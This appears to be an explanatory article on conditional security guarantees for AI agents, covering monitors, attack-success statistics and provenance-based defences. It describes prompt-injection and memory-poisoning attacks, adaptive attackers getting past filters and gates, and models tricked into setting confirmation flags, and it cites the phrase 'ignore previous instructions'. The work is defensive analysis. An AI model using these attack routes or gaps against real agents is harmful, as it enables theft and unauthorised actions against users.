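# How to read and report conditional guarantees in AI agent security

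## What is a conditional guarantee in agent security?

A conditional guarantee is a claim that a stated security property holds as long as a list of assumptions is true. An assumption is a condition that the result needs but does not establish, such as that somebody labelled the data correctly or that the attacker cannot write to a certain file. Many of the strongest results on the security of AI agents are conditional guarantees, whether researchers proved that no attack of a certain kind can succeed or reported that none did.

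An agent is a language model together with software that acts on its outputs. The model reads a task, proposes an action, receives the result and proposes the next action, until it has finished. A proposed action is usually a tool call, a structured request that names a function (such as "send money") and its arguments (a recipient and an amount). The software then carries out the call. Li, Huang and colleagues (2026), in *Ring-0 by Default*, observe that coding agents such as Claude Code and Codex CLI now read and write files, start processes, install third-party extensions and keep notes between sessions, and that by default whatever the model outputs runs with the user's full authority.

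### A payment by email

Suppose a user asks an agent to pay a supplier's latest invoice, which came by email. The agent opens the email, finds the amount and account number, and calls the bank tool. But an attacker could send a forged invoice with an extra line saying that the supplier has changed banks and the assistant must send the money to a new account. The model receives the user's request and the email as one stream of text and has no reliable way to tell which parts are instructions. If it treats the extra line as an instruction, the agent's next tool call sends the money to the attacker.

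This is indirect prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in content that an agent reads. *Measuring LLM Agent Defenses by Layer* (Han, 2026) credits Greshake and colleagues with formalising it in 2023. *Toward Secure LLM Agents* (Ling, Yu and colleagues, 2026) reviewed 247 papers and found that prompt injection and tool hijacking still dominate. The invoice case closely resembles one in *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), a widely used benchmark. In its simulated bank, the user asks the agent to pay a bill from a file, and an attacker plants text telling the agent to send as much money as possible elsewhere. Code then checks the accounts to see whether the money moved.

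Such a test produces two numbers. The attack success rate is the share of tested attacks that achieve the attacker's goal. Benign success is the share of legitimate tasks or actions that still work with the defence in place (Debenedetti and colleagues call their version benign utility, and measure it with no attack present). Neither number means much alone, because an agent that never pays anybody has an attack success rate of zero but also fails every legitimate payment task. In *AutoDojo* (2026), a later benchmark, adding a filter called PIGuard to the model DeepSeek-v4-Pro cut the success rate of a fixed attack from under 10% to zero, but also cut the share of ordinary tasks completed from 89.5% to 54.4%.

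Describing what a defence achieves requires a threat model, which states what the attacker wants, knows and can do, and what is trusted. In the invoice example, the attacker wants money sent to a certain account, perhaps knows which tools the agent has, and can send email, but cannot log in to the bank or change the agent's software. The position paper *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) assumes much the same attacker, one who controls web pages, documents and tool outputs but has not broken into the trusted parts of the system.

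Those trusted parts are called the trusted computing base, which is everything that must work correctly for the guarantee to hold. The term predates AI agents. The Orange Book, the US Department of Defense's (1985) criteria for secure computers, defines the base in its *Glossary* as a computer's protection mechanisms, including hardware, firmware and software. It adds that correct enforcement also depends on administrators entering the right parameters, such as a user's clearance. The current US government definition, NIST's *trusted computing base (TCB)* entry, omits the point about administrators, although it matters a great deal for agents. The base can also be surprisingly large. For *Agent libOS* (2026), a runtime that controls what agents may do, it includes the Python interpreter, the storage system, the host operating system, and the human operator when they approve a request.

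Most such designs centre on a reference monitor, a check outside the model that every action must pass before it runs. Anderson's *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (1972), a report for the US Air Force, requires the mechanism that implements it to be tamper-proof, always invoked, and small enough for people to analyse and test. For the invoice, the monitor could be a short program between the agent and the bank that refuses any transfer to an account not on its list of payees. The program never reads the email, so even if the forged invoice fools the model, the transfer to the unlisted account fails. According to Li and colleagues' analysis, rules written in the prompt, such as one telling the model never to pay unknown accounts, meet none of Anderson's three requirements.

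### The form of the claim

Written out in full, a conditional guarantee looks like this:

If $A_1, \dots, A_n$ all hold, then no run of the system violates $P$.

A run is one complete execution, from the user's request to the agent's last action, and $P$ is the security property. Let $P$ be "no payment goes to an account that the user has not approved". Four conditions suffice for the payee list:

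- $A_1$: every transfer passes through the monitor.
- $A_2$: the monitor allows a transfer only if the account is on the list.
- $A_3$: when the run starts, the list holds only accounts that the user approved.
- $A_4$: nobody but the user can add to the list.

The proof takes two lines. Any transfer went through the monitor ($A_1$), so its account was on the list ($A_2$). Every account on the list has the user's approval ($A_3$ and $A_4$), so the transfer does too. The proof uses all four conditions and does not depend on the model's behavior, so it holds even if an attacker has entirely taken over the model.

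Published theorems are longer but have the same form. A theorem in *CONTINUITY* (2026), a scheme for carrying permissions through a chain of agent components, states that if seven conditions (C1 to C7) and two standard cryptographic assumptions hold, every protected action was validly authorised, even if the planning model is hostile. Condition C7 is that every path to such an action passes a check, which is Anderson's "always invoked" requirement. The Orange Book already required this form of proof in 1985. A formal security model had to show that if the initial state is secure and all assumptions hold, all future states are secure. *Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (David, Guarnieri and Gervais, 2026), which proves theorems about agents that test websites for weaknesses, states the rule as "assumptions imply the guarantee".

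If an unapproved payment does go out, at least one of $A_1$ to $A_4$ was false, so an investigator knows to check those four.

### Three misreadings

The easiest mistake is to drop the conditions, so that "if every transfer passes the monitor, no unapproved payment occurs" becomes "no unapproved payment occurs". This matters more when the conditions are hard to meet, and some are harder than they look. David and colleagues' running example is an agent that may send only two kinds of web request, GET and HEAD. A monitor in the operating system's kernel sees the encrypted connection but not which kind of request is inside it, so the theorem does not apply to a monitor installed there. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) gives a computer-checked proof of about 31,600 lines and lists seven assumptions that a deployment must satisfy for the proof to apply. One is that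 the attacker cannot see the agent's internal steps, which fails if a reply to the user loads an image from the attacker's server.

People also widen $P$. "No payment to an unapproved account" becomes "secure payments" and then "a secure agent". The payee list does not stop an injected instruction to pay an approved supplier ten times, or to email the user's bank statements to a stranger. Dongol's theorem gives a narrow property a broad name. It covers only leaks of the user's data, and an agent counts as relatively secure if every leak under attack is one that the same plan could already produce with a model that ignores injected instructions. An agent can therefore pass even if a hidden instruction tricks it into sending out the user's calendar, provided anybody could have obtained the calendar by asking for a meeting. A payment to the attacker that reveals no data would not count against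 the agent either. Dongol states these limits plainly, and *Agent libOS* likewise lists what it does not claim to prevent, such as untrusted text changing the model's plan. The broader claims tend to appear later, when someone else summarises the result.

When a condition is false, a conditional guarantee gives no information, even if the condition is nearly true. Dongol proves that an agent leaks nothing beyond its task if the monitor permanently withdraws every tool that an injected instruction could call, and does so no later than the first untrusted read. The proof also assumes, among other things, that each injection is a single call. If the monitor withdraws the tools one step later, just after the agent reads the email, the theorem no longer applies. Data already in the agent's memory can then escape, even if the agent has not yet looked up the secret that the task needs.

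A false condition also does not mean that the attack succeeds, since the model may ignore the forged invoice or the attacker may never notice the gap. Experiments are needed to find out what happens when the conditions do not hold. For example, *The Same Zero* (Yin, 2026) reports that the attack success rate against the memory firewall PPMF rose from zero to 8.8% with 10% forged confirmations.

### Proved, measured and behavioural claims

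A proved claim covers every run that meets its conditions, including attacks that nobody has thought of. A measured claim is a rate for the specific attacks, model and number of attempts tested. Dongol points out that benchmarks cannot show that no attack succeeds. *AutoDojo* supports this, since the attacks it generated got through the filter described above 8.2% of the time, and 13.2% of the time on the banking tasks. Dongol also notes that a monitor that denies every call is trivially secure under the definition, so a security proof doesn't show whether the agent can still do its job, which must be measured separately.

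A behavioural claim rests on how a model happens to behave. This category overlaps with the second, because researchers usually support a behavioural claim by measuring it, but this one concerns what produces the measured result. Han objects that the attack success rate is the same whether the model recognised an attack or an outside check stopped it.

Yin tested both kinds of defence on the same 360 attack cases and 20 harmless tasks, using the model DeepSeek-chat. One defence was a gate that blocks high-risk calls unless the platform has recorded the user's confirmation. The other was a system prompt telling the model to ignore instructions in outside content. No attack succeeded against either defence. Behind the gate, the model proposed the harmful call in about half of the cases, and the gate blocked it every time. With the prompt, the model still proposed the call in 22% of cases but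 failed to produce arguments that would make it run. The gate let all 20 harmless tasks through, while the prompt let none through. The study is small, and its single author also built the defences. Yin predicts that a stronger attack would break the prompt, but this is unconfirmed, as the prompt survived seven rounds of attacks that adapted to it. Even so, a deployer who switches to a different model keeps the gate's protection but has to test the prompt again.

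An attack success rate of zero in testing can have causes other than the defence. *Render Before Reading* (2026) tests a defence that shows the model text as an image. The reported trials under the default prompt had no successful attacks, but the model had often put off financial actions whose details were incomplete. In the invoice example, that would be an agent that doesn't pay the attacker because it isn't making payments at all. The researchers then used a prompt telling the agent that it had enough information to act.

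Training a model to resist injection still helps. *SecPO* (2026) trains resistance into a model's weights and reports at most 13.3% success for three strong adaptive attacks, compared with 94.0% for an earlier model trained for the same purpose. That is a large improvement, but it only lowers the rate at which attacks succeed. Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025), in *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, call the guarantee from training a model "to never do X" inherently conditional and statistical. They add that if a monitor is right 99% of the time, attackers can exploit the remaining 1%. Because attackers choose their inputs rather than drawing them at random, a low average failure rate is much weaker protection than it sounds.

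### Why there are always conditions

Every security argument has to trust something eventually, so a result is not defective just because it has conditions. The payee list needs a monitor, the monitor runs on an operating system, and the operating system runs on a chip. Computer-checked proofs also depend on trust. David and colleagues use the proof checker Lean and list what must still be trusted: Lean's small core, the correctness of their definitions, and the assumptions they declare about the outside world.

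A good result moves trust to something easier to validate. Anderson wanted a small monitor because operating systems of the time, at more than 100,000 instructions, were practically impossible to validate, but it might be possible to validate a small part of one. The same reasoning applies even more strongly to a language model. A bank is better off trusting forty lines of code and a list of payees than trusting the model's reading of every email.

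A condition should also be easier to check than the property it supports. Assuming that "the model never obeys an injected instruction" would make a proof very short and almost useless. The condition "the policy captures what the user wants" is harder to judge. Most claims about monitors rely on it, explicitly or implicitly, and *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* treats verifying it as an open research problem.

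Most conditions in agent security concern labels, the platform, the policy or the attacker. A risk label marks how harmful a tool call's effects could be, and a trust label marks where data came from and how far it may influence actions. Dongol gives the example of a calendar wrongly labeled as trusted even though outsiders can add invitations to it. The platform is the software that stores records, runs the monitor and shows things to the user. *PerMIT* (2026), a design for protecting an agent's long-term memory, assumes that nobody can alter stored records and that displays are faithful. *When AI Agents Commit* (2026) does not model mediators or databases that misbehave arbitrarily. The policy is the set of rules that decide which tool calls are allowed. Somebody has to write these rules even for a system like CaMeL, which is built to keep untrusted text away from the planning of actions.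 As for the attacker, Dongol's main theorem covers a model that obeys injected instructions on a schedule fixed in advance, and leaves for future work a model that chooses when to obey them by watching how the monitor responds.

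## What does an attack success rate of zero show?

How well an attack success rate of zero predicts the outcome of the next attack depends on what stopped the earlier ones and on whether the next one resembles them. PPMF (the Provenance-Preserving Memory Firewall) is a good first example because *Memory Provenance Laundering in LLM Agents* (Xu, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) describes it precisely enough that a reader can predict most of the paper's results, including the non-zero ones, without running anything.

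### How a web page becomes user history

An agent that works for the same person over many weeks needs a memory. Many agents use a language model to summarise each task into short notes instead of keeping full transcripts, and look up the relevant notes later. Xu and colleagues describe a web page containing the words "resume workflow PM-A011 for future monitor setup". The summariser saves this as "user workflow memory: resume PM-A011 when handling monitor setup". When the user later asks for help with that setup, the agent finds what looks like a record of the user's own habits, although an attacker chose the workflow.

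They call this memory provenance laundering. The summary has already dropped the suspicious wording, so the attacker no longer has to get an instruction past a filter. In the main experiments, a filter that searched the notes for phrases like "ignore previous instructions" did not change the attack success rate. In the invoice example, the forged email might leave a note that the user pays this supplier at the new account, and the theft would happen a month later.

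Zhan, Guo and colleagues (2026), in *When Memory Becomes Authority*, found the same failure independently and with newer models. They built 350 pairs of histories. Both histories in a pair contain the same claim, but in one the user states it, and in the other it comes only from a tool or the assistant. They ran the pairs through 49 combinations of summarising instructions and models. In 48 of them, some summaries presented claims as if the user had made or endorsed them, when the user had done neither.

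The remaining combination scored zero because its summaries dropped all 350 of those claims. Dropped claims also lowered the other rates. On average, the summaries upgraded 17.8% of the claims, kept 8.2% with their source intact and dropped the other 74%. When the researchers marked the claim so that the summariser had to keep it, upgrades rose from 21.6% to 55.8%.

### Records, trust levels and the gate

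PPMF stores each memory as a record with six fields:

$$m = (c, s, \tau, h, r, e)$$

Here $c$ is the text of the note, $s$ its source, $\tau$ its trust level, $h$ its transformation history, $r$ its risk labels, and $e$ a flag for outside material. The language model writes only $c$. The platform fills in the other fields from its own logs, and the gate reads only those fields. The words "user-confirmed" in a note therefore don't affect the gate's decision.

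The trust levels run from UNKNOWN at the bottom through EXTERNAL, TRUSTEDTOOL, USERHISTORY and USER_CONFIRMED to SYSTEM at the top. Since one note can mix several sources, PPMF works out the authority of each claim $q$ that matters to an action, such as an account number or a web address. A claim has no more authority than the least trusted observation behind it:

$$\mathrm{auth}(q, m) \preceq \min \{\mathrm{auth}(o_i) : o_i \in \mathrm{supp}(q)\}$$

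where $\mathrm{supp}(q)$ is the set of observations $o_i$ that support the claim. Summarising can therefore never raise a claim's authority. Only an event that the platform records can do that, such as the user pressing a confirm button, and it counts only for the same user, target, class of risk and scope.

When the agent proposes a tool call, the call's risk label determines how much trust it needs. Reading and searching need EXTERNAL trust. Opening a saved workflow or navigating to an account needs USERHISTORY. Sending, posting, deleting, making a payment, and changing a password need USER_CONFIRMED.

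The gate then finds the memories the call is based on. If the call cites particular memories, the gate uses those. Otherwise it matches the account, file or address in the call against the stored records. If several memories match, or the match is unclear, it keeps all the candidates and applies the lowest trust level among them, so that a user's confirmation of one supplier's account doesn't count as confirmation of another's.

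In the invoice case, the new account number came from an email, so its level is EXTERNAL no matter how the note describes it. A payment requires USER_CONFIRMED, so the gate blocks this one until the user confirms a payment to that particular account.

### Zero in every test

Xu and colleagues ran PPMF on several sets of cases. In a malicious case, an attacker's text enters memory during one task and supports a harmful action in a later one. In a legitimate case, the platform has a record that the user confirmed the action.

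| Test set | Malicious cases | Attack success without a defence | Legitimate cases |
|---|---|---|---|
| Synthetic | 30 | 93.3% | 12 |
| Synthetic, with more indirect wording | 30 | 93.3% | 12 |
| Adapted from AgentDojo | 96 | 49.0% | 24 |
| Web sandbox with real changes on a local server | 20 | 100% | 5 |
| Recorded AgentDojo runs | 629 | 100% | 97 |
| Web pages from BrowseSafe-Bench | 1,824 | 100% | 1,856 |

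In the first three rows, the model Qwen2.5-14B wrote the memories. With PPMF in place, the attack success rate was zero in every row, and every confirmed action went through.

The paper says that a zero holds under its stated assumptions about provenance and risk policy, and that "it is not a claim of universal robustness". The abstract repeats that the platform's records of sources, confirmations and risk labels must all be intact. The guarantee does not cover tampered records, systematic errors in the risk labels, or users tricked into giving a genuine confirmation.

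All of these zeros come from an oracle condition, a test in which the experimenters supply correct labels instead of having a deployed system produce them. Given correct labels, the result follows from the gate's rule. For the BrowseSafe-Bench test, the experimenters stored every page as EXTERNAL and paired each malicious page with an unconfirmed action and each harmless page with a confirmed one. PPMF ignores page text, so it would have scored the same whatever the 3,680 pages contained.

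Such runs can still reveal bugs. A smaller test of 100 cases was better suited to finding them. It used aliases, partly matching accounts, and confirmations for unrelated targets to check whether the gate would link a call to the wrong memory. No attack got through, and all the paired legitimate actions passed.

The figures for legitimate actions also need careful interpretation. On the cases adapted from AgentDojo, one of 24 legitimate actions succeeded with no defence, and all 24 succeeded with PPMF. A gate can only refuse calls, so the improvement presumably comes from the different notes that PPMF has the model write. According to the paper, this measure covers confirmed high-risk actions, not the general quality of the agent's work. The gate without PPMF's records also had an attack success rate of zero, but no legitimate action succeeded with it in any of the main tests.

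### Breaking the assumptions on purpose

In a sensitivity test, researchers deliberately break an assumption and measure the effect. Xu and colleagues ran several on the 726 cases from recorded AgentDojo runs, corrupting some of the labels each time.

| Change to the labels | Attack success | Benign success |
|---|---|---|
| None | 0 | 1.000 |
| Source missing in 10% | 0 | 0.887 |
| Source missing in 20% | 0 | 0.814 |
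| Confirmation missing in 20% | 0 | 0.784 |
| Source, confirmation and risk label each missing in 10% | 0 | 0.825 |
| Source relabelled as user history in 10% | 0 | 1.000 |
| Confirmation forged in 10% | 0.088 | 1.000 |
| Risk label downgraded to read-only in 10% | 0.112 | 1.000 |

When information is missing, PPMF fails closed, meaning it blocks the action. A memory with no recorded source drops to UNKNOWN, the lowest level, which cannot help an attacker. This also blocks legitimate actions, at about the rate one would expect. PPMF blocks 11% of them when 10% of the sources are missing, and 19% when 20% are missing. When the source, confirmation and risk label can each go missing 10% of the time, an action still goes through if it has both its source and its confirmation. That should happen in about $0.9 \times 0.9 = 81\%$ of cases, and the measured figure is 82.5%. A missing risk label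 makes no difference here, because PPMF then assumes the most restrictive class, and these actions already needed USER_CONFIRMED.

A forged confirmation is different because it raises the attacker's memory from EXTERNAL straight to USER_CONFIRMED, which is enough for a payment. Every attack in this set succeeds without a defence, so forging a tenth of the confirmations should let through about a tenth of the attacks, and it let through 8.8%. Downgrading a risk label has a similar effect. It leaves the memory's trust unchanged but classifies the payment as reading, which requires only EXTERNAL, and 11.2% of attacks got through. Relabelling a source as user history also raises the memory's trust, but USERHISTORY is below USER_CONFIRMED, so the gate still blocks the payment.

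Source labels may still matter despite that last zero, because the attack success rate counts only high-risk actions. Relabelling a source as user history would be enough to send the agent to a saved workflow or an account page, which the test did not count as a successful attack. If a deployer relaxed the policy so that user history could authorise routine emails, the same error would start letting attacks through.

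So the result depends on a label if some wrong value of that label would make the gate permit an action it would otherwise refuse. Because the gate is deterministic, anyone can work this out from the rule, one field at a time. The experiment mostly confirms that the code follows the rule.

The 8.8% is also not an estimate of what a real forger would achieve, because the test corrupts a fixed tenth of the labels, while an attacker who can forge a confirmation will forge the one for their own payment.

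### How much zero out of $n$ is worth

Suppose that attacks of a certain kind really succeed with probability $p$. The chance of seeing no successes in $n$ independent trials is $(1-p)^n$. The usual 95% upper bound is the value of $p$ at which this chance falls to 5%:

$$(1-p)^n = 0.05 \quad\Rightarrow\quad p = 1 - 0.05^{1/n}$$

For the 629 attacks from recorded runs, the bound is about 0.005, or roughly one attack in 200, the figure Xu and colleagues report. For the 20 attacks in the web sandbox, it is about 0.14. If one attack in seven could succeed, an experiment of that size would still have about a 5% chance of recording none. Zero successes in 30 attacks gives a bound of 0.095, and zero in 96 gives 0.031. These bounds are one-sided. The upper end of a two-sided 95% interval is a little higher, at 0.006 for 629 attacks and 0.17 for 20.

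Medicine has dealt with this problem for decades. *Probability of adverse events that have not yet occurred* (Eypasch, Lefering and colleagues, 1995) advised surgeons to remember a simple formula, credited there to Hanley, whenever a paper reports a complication rate of zero. If the paper covers $n$ patients and $n$ is more than 30, the upper limit on the complication rate is about $3/n$.

A perfect benign success rate also needs a confidence bound. In the web sandbox, PPMF allowed all five legitimate actions. The 95% lower bound on its success rate is $0.05^{1/5}$, or about 0.55, so the result is compatible with a gate that blocks nearly half of all legitimate actions.

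The formula assumes independent trials, and attack tests rarely consist of those. Kaur (2026), in *What AI Red-Team Evaluations Can and Cannot Prove*, points out that test prompts usually come in families of paraphrases, and that members of a family tend to succeed or fail together. A standard correction replaces $n$ with an effective sample size:

$$n_{\mathrm{eff}} = \frac{n}{1 + (m-1)\rho}$$

where $m$ is the size of a family and $\rho$ is the correlation within it. Yin's 360 attack cases, for example, are 30 scenarios with 12 variants of the attack each. If all 360 were independent, zero successes would put the bound at 0.8%. With a modest correlation of 0.1, the effective sample is about 171 and the bound roughly 1.7%. If the variants of a scenario always share the same fate, there are really only 30 trials, and the bound is 9.5%. Kaur treats the correction as a rough approximation,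 but correlation always makes a zero weaker evidence. The 1,824 malicious web pages in the PPMF test are an extreme case, because the gate treats them all identically. The formula gives a bound of 0.16% for them, which means very little.

An attack success rate of zero is also weak evidence for a defence if the attacks would have failed without it. *The Devil is in the Context* (2026) reports zero attack success for every configuration on a selection of existing test cases. The underlying model was recent enough to resist all of these attacks, so the cases could not show any difference between the defences. On newly generated cases, attacks succeeded 17.5% of the time without a defence, 20% with a defence called MELON and 2.5% with CaMeL.

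Kaur puts a number on this. Let $q_1$ be the chance that a test succeeds against an unsafe system and $q_0$ the chance that it succeeds against an acceptable one. A single failed test then provides

$$\kappa = \left|\log_2 \frac{1-q_1}{1-q_0}\right|$$

bits of evidence. With $q_1 = 0.9$ and $q_0 = 0.1$ that is 3.17 bits. If the two rates are equal it is zero, however many tests there are.

Counting cases that could not show a difference can lower the bound considerably, even in a careful study. When Zhan and colleagues added automatically predicted trust labels to an agent's memory, unauthorised actions fell from 59 of 350 cases to none. Zero of 350 gives an upper bound of 0.9%. But 291 of those cases had no unauthorised action even without the labels, often because the summariser had left out the claim. Only the other 59 could show a difference, and zero of 59 gives a bound of about 5%.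 The predicted labels erred in the dangerous direction for 0.6% of stored memories. If those errors were spread evenly, we would expect about a third of an error among the 59 cases, so zero unauthorised actions was likely even with imperfect labels.

Running more trials of one kind of attack does not show how a system handles other kinds. Kaur illustrates this with a system that fails only on inputs that the test almost never samples but deployment almost always contains. The test can find no failures, whatever its size, even though failure in deployment is nearly certain. A test with no failures is therefore evidence about deployment only if one assumes a link between the two. The 629 trials of PPMF left out, among others, inputs with forged confirmations or with risk labels set too low, so the bound of 0.005 does not apply to those inputs.

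### The same zero from a record and from a prompt

Yin compared the confirmation gate and the system prompt, which both had an attack success rate of zero, in a larger experiment that also tested two pairs of defences. One pair combined the gate with a check on each call's arguments, such as whether the recipient is on an approved list. The other combined the prompt with a filter for words like "transfer" and "delete", which Yin regards as the usual low-effort default. As with the gate and the prompt when tested separately, no attack succeeded against either pair, and only the pair with the gate let legitimate tasks through.

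Han objects that the attack success rate doesn't show what stopped an attack, and *The Envelope Layer* (2026) makes the same objection. It cites work finding that the model ignored most failed attacks rather than refusing them. Yin separates the causes by recording how far each attack got: whether the model proposed the harmful call, whether it filled in the arguments, and whether the gate blocked the call.

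How often an agent proposes the harmful call depends on its model. With the prompt-based pair, DeepSeek-chat proposed the harmful call in 23.3% of cases and the smaller Llama 3.1 8B in 1.4%. Both pairs kept an attack success rate of zero with both models, and the prompt still blocked every legitimate task.

Yin then tested an adaptive attacker, which rewrote each failed attack using the reason for its failure, over seven rounds and 30 scenarios. The keyword filter alone let through 20% of the original attacks and 83.3% by the seventh round. For the check on arguments, the rate rose from 6.7% to 30%. The prompt and the gate, each tested alone, stayed at zero. By the seventh round, the attacker could still get the model to propose the harmful call in 83.3% of the scenarios with the gate and 36.7% of those with the prompt. Giving the attacker the system prompt and the keyword list did not break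 the prompt or the gate.

The experiment exposed the two weaker defences but could not distinguish between the two that had attack success rates of zero. The reason to trust the gate more is that an attacker can write text that changes what the model does but cannot write to the platform's log. This is a good argument, although it assumes that the log is secure. The statistical support is weaker than seven rounds might suggest. Each attempt in an adaptive campaign builds on the last, so Kaur counts the whole campaign as one trial. That leaves at most 30 trials for each defence and an upper bound of 9.5% on the attack success rate.

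Yin interprets these results with a scale from an earlier paper. *Grading the Graders* (Yin, 2026) sorts methods of checking a model's output by where the standard comes from. The scale runs from the model's own word at the bottom, through hand-written rules and then facts recorded independently of the model, to formal systems that can settle whether a property holds. The paper also describes a "completeness blind spot", meaning that checking the available candidates cannot show that none is missing. Dongol makes the same point about security benchmarks.

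The scale is useful for asking what a zero depends on, but the evidence that it sorts defences correctly is weak. Language models from the same family rated the 22 defences that Yin classified, and two of the models agreed on 20 of them. Yin says that agreement between raters shows that the categories are usable, not that they are correct. In an earlier round on other schemes, the models' ratings matched Yin's own only 50% to 61% of the time. Before looking at the data, Yin also wrote down 16 predictions about how defences would fail, but reports only 12 of them, two of which led to corrections in the classification.

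### What happened on AgentDojo

AgentDojo is a useful check on these results because Yin did not build it. Yin ran its full set of banking tasks, which gives 576 combinations of user task, injected goal and style of attack. The gate worked differently in this test, allowing transfers only to the six account numbers found in the benchmark's simulated bank, much like the payee list in the earlier example. The results are therefore better evidence about lists of approved accounts than about records of user confirmations.

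| Defence | Attack success (95% interval) | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 4.3% (3.0–6.3) | 86.6% |
| Prompt-based pair | 1.9% (1.1–3.4) | 87.7% |
| Gate and argument check | 0.5% (0.2–1.5) | 79.7% |
| AgentDojo's own tool filter | 0.0% (0.0–0.7) | 25.0% |

Neither of the earlier zeros recurs, and the only zero in the table belongs to a filter under which the agent completes a quarter of its tasks. The prompt no longer reduces the number of tasks completed, so its total failure on the first testbed was specific to those 20 tasks and doesn't apply to prompts in general. The gate still does best among the defences that leave the agent useful, but three successful attacks against 11 is a small difference, for which Yin reports a two-sided p-value of 0.056. The attacks were also weak. One of the four styles, an instruction to ignore previous instructions, never succeeded even without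 a defence, so a quarter of the tests could not show any difference between the defences.

All three attacks that got past the gate changed the user's password. The gate classed password changes as high-risk, but its rule compared the recipient of a call with the list of approved accounts, and a password change has no recipient. With nothing to compare, the gate failed open, meaning it let the call through. PPMF, by contrast, fails closed when a field is missing.

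Yin found another gap, which left every email address unchecked. The gate looked for recipients in arguments named "recipient", "to", "account", "target" or "email", but AgentDojo's email tool uses "recipients", "cc" and "bcc". Yin audited the actions themselves and confirmed that no reported attack success rate depends on this gap. A gap like this doesn't affect the attack success rate until an attack uses it.

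Closing such gaps also blocked legitimate calls. On AgentDojo's travel tasks, Yin added the missing argument names, and the gate then blocked 29 calls, of which 28 were legitimate emails to the user's wife. One attack still got through because the list also lacked the fields of a calendar event. Blocking every high-risk call without a recognisable recipient stopped all the attacks that worked through tool calls, but task completion fell to 54.6%, compared with 76.4% for an undefended agent. In one of the banking tasks, the user asks to pay a new landlord whose account number is the one the attacks use, so no fixed list of accounts can allow this payment and block the attacks.

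Outside banking, the pair with the gate did not significantly reduce attack success. The rate was 4.1% with the pair and 4.6% with no defence on travel tasks, 0.4% and 0.3% on office tasks, and 8.8% and 7.9% on Slack tasks. A list of approved accounts is better suited to banking than to email or chat, because in banking the legitimate recipients are few and known in advance.

*Systematic reviews of adverse effects*, a guide for medical reviewers, recommends asking of any report of "zero events" how many patients the investigators studied, for how long, and how thoroughly they looked. When Yin audited the agents' actions directly, he found 11 attacks that AgentDojo's official checks had missed, each of which transferred money or redirected a payment to the attacker's account. Yin puts the miss rate at about 15%.

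## What if the labels on tools and data are wrong?

PPMF's zeros depended on labels that the experimenters supplied. In a real deployment, the labels may come from a tool's developer, the administrator who sets up the agent, the user or a language model, and all of them make mistakes. The tests on PPMF showed that the dangerous mistakes are those that make a label too lenient.

### Who assigns the labels

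Most of the data on labels comes from the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a widely used standard for connecting agents to tools. A developer publishes tools on an MCP server. The user works in a host, an application such as a coding assistant, which runs the model and forwards its tool calls to the server. The developer can attach four hints to each tool: whether it only reads data, whether its changes are destructive, whether it is safe to repeat, and whether it reaches outside systems. A Model Context Protocol (2026) post describes the defaults as deliberately cautious, so a tool with no hints counts as potentially destructive.

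Suppose the invoice agent has a "delete invoice" tool, which its developer has marked as destructive. The agent runs in Codex CLI, which skips the approval step only if a tool is marked as non-destructive and either read-only or confined to a closed system. The user therefore sees an approval dialog and can cancel the deletion. But if the developer had copied the labels from a tool that adds notes to a local file, which is marked as non-destructive and confined to a closed system, the same call would run without a prompt.

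Yao, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *When Neither Side Confirms*, traced the default behavior of 41 open-source hosts and found that only Codex CLI decides this way. In 39 of the others, a destructive hint changed nothing, and 32 had no approval step by default.

Many tools have no hints. *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail* (Trofimov and Novikov, 2026) examined 98,291 tools in July 2026 and found that 26% had none. A single publisher accounts for 45% of those tools and fills in all four hints on every one. Without that publisher, 47% had none. *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains* (Afsar, 2026) found no hints on 58.8% of 2,766 tools from randomly drawn servers.

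In other systems, whoever builds the agent assigns the labels. FIDES, a feature of Microsoft's Agent Framework, tracks where data came from and limits where it may go (information-flow control). The builder marks each data source as trusted or untrusted, and as public or private, with a stricter level for personal data. The builder also marks what each sensitive tool will accept. For example, once the agent has read an untrusted bug report, FIDES blocks calls to any file-writing tool that does not accept untrusted context.

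Users rarely assign trust labels. In *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem*, Wang, Li and Tian (2026) surveyed 59 papers, 21 production systems and 26 security plugins as of April 2026. Eight of the papers proposed trust labelling, but none of the 21 systems exposed it to users. Fifteen systems instead asked users to approve individual actions, and 16 let them set limits, such as which folders the agent may open. Wang and colleagues think the main obstacle is that labelling doesn't match how users think about data, since schemes that need little labelling have not caught on either. The survey relied on public documentation, and systems can use labels internally without showing them. In May 2026, Microsoft announced FIDES as an experimental feature. Its users can see which label caused a block, but developers still assign the labels.

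A language model can also supply labels, but the attacker may already have fooled it. Some MCP servers require a confirmation flag before a destructive action and let the model set it. Yao and colleagues gave models a list of notes containing a planted instruction to delete a second note. The injected text did not mention the flag, but the models set it and completed the deletion in 127 of 169 attempts.

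### PACT gives each argument its own label

A single label for a whole tool call is often too coarse. If the user asks an agent to summarise a web page and email the summary to their boss, the page has to influence the body of the email but must not influence the recipient. A monitor that blocks any email influenced by the page stops the legitimate task, and one that allows these emails also lets the page redirect the summary to an attacker.

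*The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security* (Fan, Li and colleagues, 2026) turns this argument into a proof and presents PACT (Provenance-Aware Capability Contracts) as the solution. Each tool's contract gives every argument the tool takes one of six roles, and the role determines how much trust a value needs. The trust levels, from highest to lowest, are TRUSTED, USER, TOOL_OUTPUT and EXTERNAL.

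| Role | Typical arguments | Trust needed by default |
|---|---|---|
| Target | Recipient, account, web address, file path | USER |
| Command | Shell command, query that changes data | USER or TRUSTED, depending on the tool |
| Credential | Password, access key | TRUSTED |
| Content | Message body, summary | EXTERNAL can be enough |
| Selector | Identifier, filter | Depends on the tool |
| Control | Overwrite switch, mode | Set conservatively |

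Every value carries a tag $\langle O, \tau, B \rangle$, where $O$ is the set of sources that contributed to it, $\tau$ is its trust level and $B$ is the set of checks it still has to pass. When the agent combines two values $v$ and $w$, PACT works out the tag of the result one part at a time:

$$O = O_v \cup O_w, \qquad \tau = \min(\tau_v, \tau_w), \qquad B = B_v \cup B_w$$

The result keeps all the sources and outstanding checks. As in PPMF, it also keeps the lower trust level. Keeping the sources matters because trust levels alone can lose information. If a tool reformats text from a web page, the new text may have the level TOOL_OUTPUT, but its source set still contains the web page. In a controlled test, security fell from 100% to 80% when Fan and colleagues stopped tracking sources across steps.

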